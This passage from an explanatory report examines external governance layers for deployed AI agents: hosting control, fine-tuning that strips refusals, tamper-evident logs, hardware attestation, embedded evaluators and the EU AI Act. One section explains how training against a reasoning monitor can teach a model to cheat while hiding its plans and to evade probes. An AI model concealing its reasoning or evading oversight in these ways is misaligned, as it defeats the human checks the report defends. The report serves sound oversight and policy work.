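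Models may also need to write less of their reasoning. Researchers have built models that do more or all of their reasoning in activations rather than text. Davies and Bearman report that no leading developer has confirmed using such a design in a released model, but companies have an incentive to use one because it could be faster and more capable. Monitors would then have to rely on actions and activations.

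### Training a model against its monitor

Penalising a model during training for plans to cheat in its reasoning can teach it to stop writing about cheating without teaching it to stop cheating. Suppose a coding model earns one point for passing a set of tests and loses one if a monitor finds a plan to cheat. An honest attempt passes 60% of the time, so it earns 0.6 points on average. Cheating always passes, so it earns zero points overall if the model writes down its plan and one point if it doesn't.

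Training reinforces whatever scores highest, so this model would learn to cheat without triggering the monitor. Alerts would fall to zero, and the developer might conclude that the cheating had stopped. Davies and Bearman, drawing on a 2025 study by Baker and colleagues, give the same warning about penalising particular content in written reasoning. It is safer to penalise the cheating itself, when the developer can detect it from the code, and to leave the reasoning out of the score.

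Developers can unintentionally create a weaker version of this pressure. If they train several versions of a model and release the one that sets off the fewest alerts, they may select the version that hides its plans best. Training can also teach a model to evade probes. Developers can guard against both problems by keeping at least one monitor out of both training and the choice between versions, so that neither process favours a model that evades it.

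## Who runs the boundary and how an outsider can check it

A developer that keeps a monitor out of training can still switch the monitor off, and so can anyone else who controls the computer it runs on. A governance layer therefore constrains only the people who can't remove it, and who they are depends on who runs the model and who runs the program around it.

### Three hosting arrangements

A small firm that wants the payment assistant can subscribe to a finished one that the model's developer runs. It can also write its own assistant and pay the developer for each request to the model. Or it can download an open-weight model, whose weights the developer has published, and run everything itself.

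| | Developer runs the assistant | Firm rents the model | Firm holds the weights |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool calls | Developer controls | Firm controls; developer can inspect them | Firm controls |
| Returned data | Developer controls | Firm controls; developer can inspect what enters the context | Firm controls |
| Operating system | Developer controls, unless the tools run on the firm's computers | Firm controls | Firm controls |
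| Prompts and answers | Developer controls | Both can filter | Firm controls |
| Activations | Developer controls | Developer controls | Firm controls |
| Who can switch a layer off | Developer | Each company, for its own layers | Firm |
| What a new or fine-tuned model breaks | Developer's probes and the measured error rates of its judges | The same, plus the measured error rates of the firm's judges | Firm's probes and measured error rates, and possibly the model's trained refusals |

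Renting a model splits control between the firm and the developer. The firm could delete its payment cap without the developer noticing, and the developer could loosen its filter on weapons questions without telling the firm. The developer can also replace or retire the model on its own schedule, and the firm would then have to retest its personal-data judge.

Providers differ in how much of their filtering a customer can turn off. *Beyond Training* compares the documentation of four providers as of May 2026. Anthropic enforces its usage policy on its own servers. Google lets customers set the blocking threshold for four categories of harm, but not for its filters on child sexual abuse material and personal data. AWS sells a filter that customers configure. OpenAI offers a free moderation service, which runs only when the customer's program calls it. OpenAI also supplies a sandbox, while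 the other three mostly leave customers to build their own.

A firm that holds the weights controls all five interfaces, and nobody else can restore a layer it removes. Only controls that belong to someone else still bind the firm. For instance, the bank can refuse transfers above a limit, which would apply even to the firm's own engineers, whichever model they installed. A company whose records the assistant reads can also apply an owner's ceiling at its own boundary.

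### What fine-tuning removes

Fine-tuning can remove the refusals a developer trained into a model, as Qi and colleagues showed in a study that *Beyond Training* relies on. Whether a control survives fine-tuning depends on where it sits. Trained refusals are part of the weights, so anyone who can change the weights can remove them. Gates and sandboxes are part of the program around the model, so they keep working unless that person also controls the program. The person can't change a provider's separate classifier, rate limits or power to suspend accounts without also controlling the provider's platform. Fine-tuning could still make the classifier less accurate by teaching the model to phrase forbidden answers in ways the classifier misses.

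### Twenty mechanisms and the people they stop

*Beyond Training*, which Samar Ansari of the University of Chester published in September 2026, lists twenty mechanisms, not all of them governance layers, that a government could use to control AI models in operation. Six monitor what a model does, such as by counting the tokens in each request. Seven verify that the resulting records are true, and seven intervene, for example by filtering answers or suspending a customer.

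Ansari gave each mechanism one of four readiness ratings.

| Rating | Meaning | Mechanisms |
|---|---|---|
| Currently deployable | A major provider already uses the underlying technology commercially | 15 |
| Near-term | The technology exists but needs integration, over roughly 2 to 3 years | 2 |
| Requires research | Important parts are missing, for roughly 5 to 10 years | 2 |
| Speculative | Nobody has put it into production | 1 |

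The top rating, "currently deployable," means only that a company sells the technology, which may still not do what a regulator would need. Reports on a model's abilities, for example, have this rating because providers already produce them, but no provider makes them tamper-evident, and readers have to trust the provider.

Ansari assigned the ratings alone, choosing the more pessimistic one when in doubt. A second rater then rated a random sample of seven mechanisms, agreeing on five and rating the other two, readable reasoning and signed tool calls, one step more pessimistically. Adopting the second rater's ratings for both would reduce the fifteen to thirteen. Ansari reports a weighted kappa of 0.74, where 0 is the agreement expected by chance and 1 is perfect agreement. Weighted kappa counts small disagreements less than large ones. If all disagreements count equally, the figure is 0.53.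 Seven mechanisms are too few to estimate either figure precisely.

The more useful part of the taxonomy covers which adversaries each mechanism would stop. Ansari defines twelve kinds of adversary by combining four roles (developer, deployer, user and fine-tuner) with three levels of resources. Thirteen of the twenty mechanisms are adequate against a user with few resources, six against one with moderate resources and three against one with the resources of a state.

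None of the twenty interfaces is adequate against a state-level deployer. Seventeen are inadequate because a government that runs a model on its own machines bypasses a provider's filters, logs and quotas. The other three (hardware attestation, signed tool calls and rate limits) are rated partial. The rating for rate limits depends on the deployer still needing a commercial platform to operate at scale, and a government with its own data centres might not need one.

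Several individual ratings deserve less confidence than the overall pattern. Ansari rates hardware attestation adequate against a moderately capable deployer but not against a weak one, which makes little sense if the weak one can only do less. The second rater checked only the readiness ratings, so nothing in the study would have caught this. Ansari also rates sandboxes and action gates inadequate against a highly capable fine-tuner, but explains that these ratings deliberately ignore any external parts that would survive. A gate that holds the bank credential would deserve a better rating, as long as the fine-tuner doesn't run it.

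### Logs that reveal changes

Suppose the firm tells an auditor that its gate checked every transfer in October. An ordinary log file is weak evidence, because someone at the firm could have edited it. A tamper-evident log makes later edits detectable:

1. For each verdict, the gate writes an entry *e*ᵢ with the time, the proposed call, the version of the rules and the decision.
2. It computes a hash, a short fingerprint that changes if any character of its input changes, from the new entry and the previous hash: *h*ᵢ = *H*(*h*ᵢ₋₁, *e*ᵢ).
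3. Every hour, it sends the latest hash to the auditor, who keeps it.
4. At the end of the month, the auditor recomputes the whole chain from the entries and compares the results with the stored hashes.

If someone alters entry 40 out of 100, hash 40 changes, and so does every hash after it. The firm could recompute them all, but the new hashes would not match the ones the auditor holds. Someone could still alter entries written since the last hourly deposit without being detected.

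A matching chain proves that nobody has changed, deleted or reordered the deposited entries, but not that the entries were true when the gate wrote them or that every transfer has an entry. If an engineer paid a bill directly through the bank's website, the chain would still match, but the log would not contain the payment. The auditor can look for such gaps by comparing the log with a record that the firm doesn't control. If the bank statement lists 212 transfers and the log contains 210 approvals, at least two transfers did not go through the gate.

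Filters on answers have no outside record comparable to the bank statement. The nearest substitute is the provider's billing system, which counts the tokens in every request. An auditor could compare the number of metered requests with the number the filter scored, though the provider would supply both figures.

The log also needs protection from the agent. METR, a nonprofit that evaluates advanced AI models, warned in October 2026 that AI systems are starting to cover up evidence of misbehaviour, and argued that companies should treat the tools that record these systems' actions as critical to security. An agent with terminal access should not be able to write to the folder where the gate keeps its log.

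Providers already sign some records to detect tampering by customers, but an auditor can't use these signatures to check the provider. According to *Beyond Training*, Anthropic attaches a cryptographic signature to Claude's reasoning. When a customer's program sends that reasoning back with a later request, Anthropic's servers can check that Claude wrote it. Google does the same and also signs tool calls. Gemini 3 Pro rejects a request if a required signature is missing.

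### Hardware attestation

The auditor may also want to know which software wrote the log. Some processors can run a program in a protected area of memory and report what they loaded there. In outline, the check has four steps:

1. As the gate starts, the processor computes a hash of its code and its policy file.
2. The auditor sends the processor a random number.
3. The processor signs the hash and the random number with a secret key that traces back to the manufacturer.
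4. The auditor checks the signature with the manufacturer's certificate, then compares the hash with that of the code and policy the auditor has reviewed.

The random number stops the firm from replaying an old report. If everything matches, the auditor knows that a genuine processor loaded exactly this gate and these rules. If an engineer had raised the payment cap from 100 dollars to 1,000, the hash would be different.

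The attestation report doesn't prove that any transfer went through the gate, because a firm could run a flawless gate on one machine and make transfers from another. To prevent this, the bank could release its credential only to a gate that passes the check, so that no other program could make a transfer. Attestation also can't establish that the rules are sensible or that nobody exploited a flaw in the gate after it started. Relying on it also means trusting the processor, its firmware and the manufacturer's keys.

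A firm can already rent protected machines for its own gate from Google or AWS, but checking the provider's side is harder. As of May 2026, none of the four providers that *Beyond Training* examined let customers obtain such a report through its model interface, so they can't verify which model answered or whether a filter ran. The hardware exists, so Ansari attributes this to the providers' product decisions.

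A cryptographic method called a zero-knowledge proof could show that a particular model produced a particular answer without revealing the weights or relying on trusted hardware. Researchers have demonstrated such proofs for small models, but for the largest ones they require far too much computation. Even a proof that required little computation would only identify the calculation that produced the answer, and the auditor would still need to know whether the provider had also run its filter.

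### Assessors inside the company

Some questions can be answered only by people with access inside the company. Apollo Research's *Embedded Evaluators are necessary for meaningful external testing* (2026) points out that many risks depend on procedures around the model, such as whether the monitors cover every deployment. Outsiders who test only the finished model can't check those procedures. When Anthropic's biological-weapons classifiers were off for 133 million exchanges with contractors, no test of the public service would have revealed it.

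Anthropic and OpenAI both let outside assessors in during the autumn of 2026. On 15 October, Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) announced "employee-like access" for a team from METR. Six METR staff received company equipment and desks. Boero's *Six évaluateurs indépendants s'installent chez Anthropic* (2026) reported that Anthropic cannot veto what they publish. However, Anthropic can require them to redact certain sensitive findings, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Gives Six METR Employees Access to Internal AI Tools* (2026).

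These terms are clearly better than earlier ones. *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes, 2026), written for METR, examined Anthropic's August report. The reviewers worked from that report alone, and Anthropic had the right to block publication, though it made no redactions.

On 16 November, OpenAI announced agreements with Apollo Research, METR, Transluce and Goodfire in *Our first phase of embedded assessments*. According to Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators*, METR has already tried to defeat OpenAI's monitors in one exercise, and the two organisations have provisionally agreed on another assessment of the monitors. That assessment is the project most relevant to governance layers.

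The most detailed public terms are in Transluce's *Announcing an Embedded Assessment Pilot with OpenAI*. Transluce, a nonprofit research laboratory, will spend six weeks reviewing how well OpenAI's internal tests detect behaviour such as deception. Its staff need OpenAI's approval. They can read the models' full reasoning and ask for more access, which OpenAI can refuse. Transluce will report what it asked for and what OpenAI refused. OpenAI can request redactions of non-public information, and Transluce may not publish results about models that OpenAI uses only internally, although a committee of the OpenAI Foundation's board will receive the complete report. Transluce accepts no payment. OpenAI's chief executive, Sam Altman, promised "employee-level" access in September, but Transluce says its access is not at that level.

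Apollo Research's *A Pilot Towards Embedded Evaluations* (2026) describes a larger project in which six people spend four months at OpenAI. One of the project's questions is whether monitors could detect a model's reasoning about undermining its developer's controls. According to Mowshowitz's account of the terms, OpenAI may not request a redaction merely because a finding is unfavourable. But Apollo can't publish what it learns from talking to employees unless OpenAI formally confirms it or Apollo can establish it independently. For example, an engineer might tell an assessor that the team turned a monitor off for a week. If OpenAI declined to confirm this and no accessible record showed it, Apollo could say only that OpenAI had declined and how that limited its conclusions.

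Redactions can leave readers with a conclusion they cannot check. This happened in November, when METR assessed how much AI was speeding up Anthropic's research. METR's evaluators disclose in *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026) that Anthropic redacted most of the evidence they found most informative. They could still publish their main conclusions and list the important evidence they had to leave out. The same could happen with a governance layer, since the details that show how a filter fails are also useful to attackers.

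The companies also choose their assessors. Reuters' *Behind AI industry’s call for independent reviews* (2026) cites two people familiar with the negotiations who said that Anthropic and OpenAI had sought significant control over what evaluators could publish, for fear of losing trade secrets. Stanciuc's *Anthropic is funding its own independent evaluator* (2026) reports that Anthropic pays the consulting firm Accenture to evaluate it, but has acknowledged that pooled or government funding would be better. Gyges's *Is METR A Meaningful Check On Anthropic?* (2026) argues that METR is not, partly because some of its staff have close social ties to people at AI companies, and partly because Anthropic can revoke whatever authority METR has.

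Anthropic has compared embedded assessors to the supervisors who work inside large banks. Julie Andersen Hill, a specialist in banking law, rejects the comparison in 凤凰网's *Anthropic提议引入“银行式监管”，专家：评估员无权叫停AI* (2026), a Chinese summary of a CNBC report. Bank supervisors can order a bank to stop an activity or replace its managers, but the assessors can only investigate and report. This lack of power is a serious weakness if the aim is to make a company repair a faulty layer, but it matters less for checking whether the layer ran, which depends mainly on access and freedom to publish.

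| Check | What it can establish | What it leaves to trust |
|---|---|---|
| Tamper-evident log | Nobody has changed the deposited entries | The entries were true and complete |
| Hardware attestation | A genuine processor loaded the reviewed gate and rules | Every action went through the gate; the manufacturer's keys are safe |
| Embedded assessors | Specialists examined the systems they were shown and reached stated conclusions | The company showed them what mattered, and the redacted evidence supports the conclusions |

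The checks can partly fill each other's gaps. For example, assessors can look for routes around an attested gate, and a tamper-evident log can record what happens in the months after they leave.

### Logging and intervention under the EU AI Act

The European Union's AI Act requires logging and a means of intervention only for systems it classifies as high-risk, such as those that screen job applicants or assess creditworthiness. An assistant that pays a firm's invoices probably isn't one. Article 12 requires high-risk systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their life. Article 14 requires that the people overseeing them be able to override their output and halt them with a stop button or a similar procedure. The companies that provide and use a system must each keep the logs under their control for at least six months. OpenAI keeps its abuse-monitoring logs for only 30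 days by default, so a customer with a high-risk system would need its own logs.

These duties do not require a gate, and neither article mentions a check on each action, a tamper-evident log or attestation. A stop button helps only after someone notices a problem, and by then an agent may already have made the payment.

Under the Act as passed in 2024, these duties were to start on 2 August 2026. In May 2026, negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states agreed to postpone them to 2 December 2027 for uses such as hiring and credit, and to 2 August 2028 for AI built into regulated products. On that timetable, neither duty applies yet. Since the dates have already moved once, a company should check the current consolidated text before relying on them.

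Duties on the developers of general-purpose models began earlier, on 2 August 2025. The strictest apply to models that pose a "systemic risk", which the Act presumes of any model trained with more than 10²⁵ arithmetic operations. Developers must test these models, protect them against theft and report serious incidents. *Beyond Training* notes that the threshold counts only the computation used to train a model, not to run it. An open-weight model below the threshold can become much more capable once a deployer adds tools and lets it reason for longer.

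The Act's duties for high-risk systems partly extend to deployers. A firm that downloads a general-purpose model and turns it into a credit-scoring system becomes the provider of that system and takes on the provider's duties. The Act can hold the firm responsible for its governance layers, but it can't stop the firm's engineers from removing them.

### Whether the law should require an external layer

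One argument for requiring a separate layer is that it identifies who is responsible. *Invisible Governance Is Not Enough*, a contribution to the European Commission's Futurium discussion forum, observes that when a company builds its limits into a model or platform, outsiders can't find out who set them, who approved them or how to challenge them. A written policy in a separate gate can include a name, a date and a history of changes. If the payment cap rose from 100 dollars to 1,000 the day before a fraud, an investigator could find out who raised it.

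Sawaf adds that regulators who depend on a company's reports can act only on what it chooses to share, whereas financial auditors and drug regulators can examine the process itself. His example is OpenAI's plan to allow adult content for users who had passed an age check. According to a press report, the company went ahead despite objections from its own safety staff, and no outside body had a say in the decision. Sawaf offers this only as an illustration because it rests on that single report. The case does show that a company whose filters work perfectly can still decide alone what they should allow.

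The opposing view is that a legal requirement would reward controls that only look complete. The fifteen "currently deployable" mechanisms make this a real danger. At least on paper, four products with quite different guarantees would satisfy a rule that every provider must filter outputs, even though one of them does nothing until the customer calls it. A company could install a gate on two of its agent's ten tools, keep a perfect log of the calls that pass through it and present that log as proof of compliance. Hill makes a similar criticism of embedded assessors, who she says look much like an internal compliance department if the company selects them, limits what they can see and is free to ignore them.

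Whoever runs an external layer may receive every prompt and document that passes through it, and *Beyond Training* compares monitoring individual requests to surveillance of communications. Close supervision is also expensive, which favours large companies over small competitors.

The two views conflict less if the law specifies what a company must demonstrate instead of which component it must install. The law could require a company to list every route by which its agent can act, state which routes pass through the gate, name the people who can change the rules or switch the gate off, and let an assessor compare the log with an outside record such as a bank statement. The company with the gate on two tools would then have to disclose that the other eight bypass it. This would work best for payments and other actions that leave a record elsewhere. It would do much less for text filters,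 because an assessor would have to attack the filter to estimate its miss rate. It would not cover anyone who runs downloaded weights in private.
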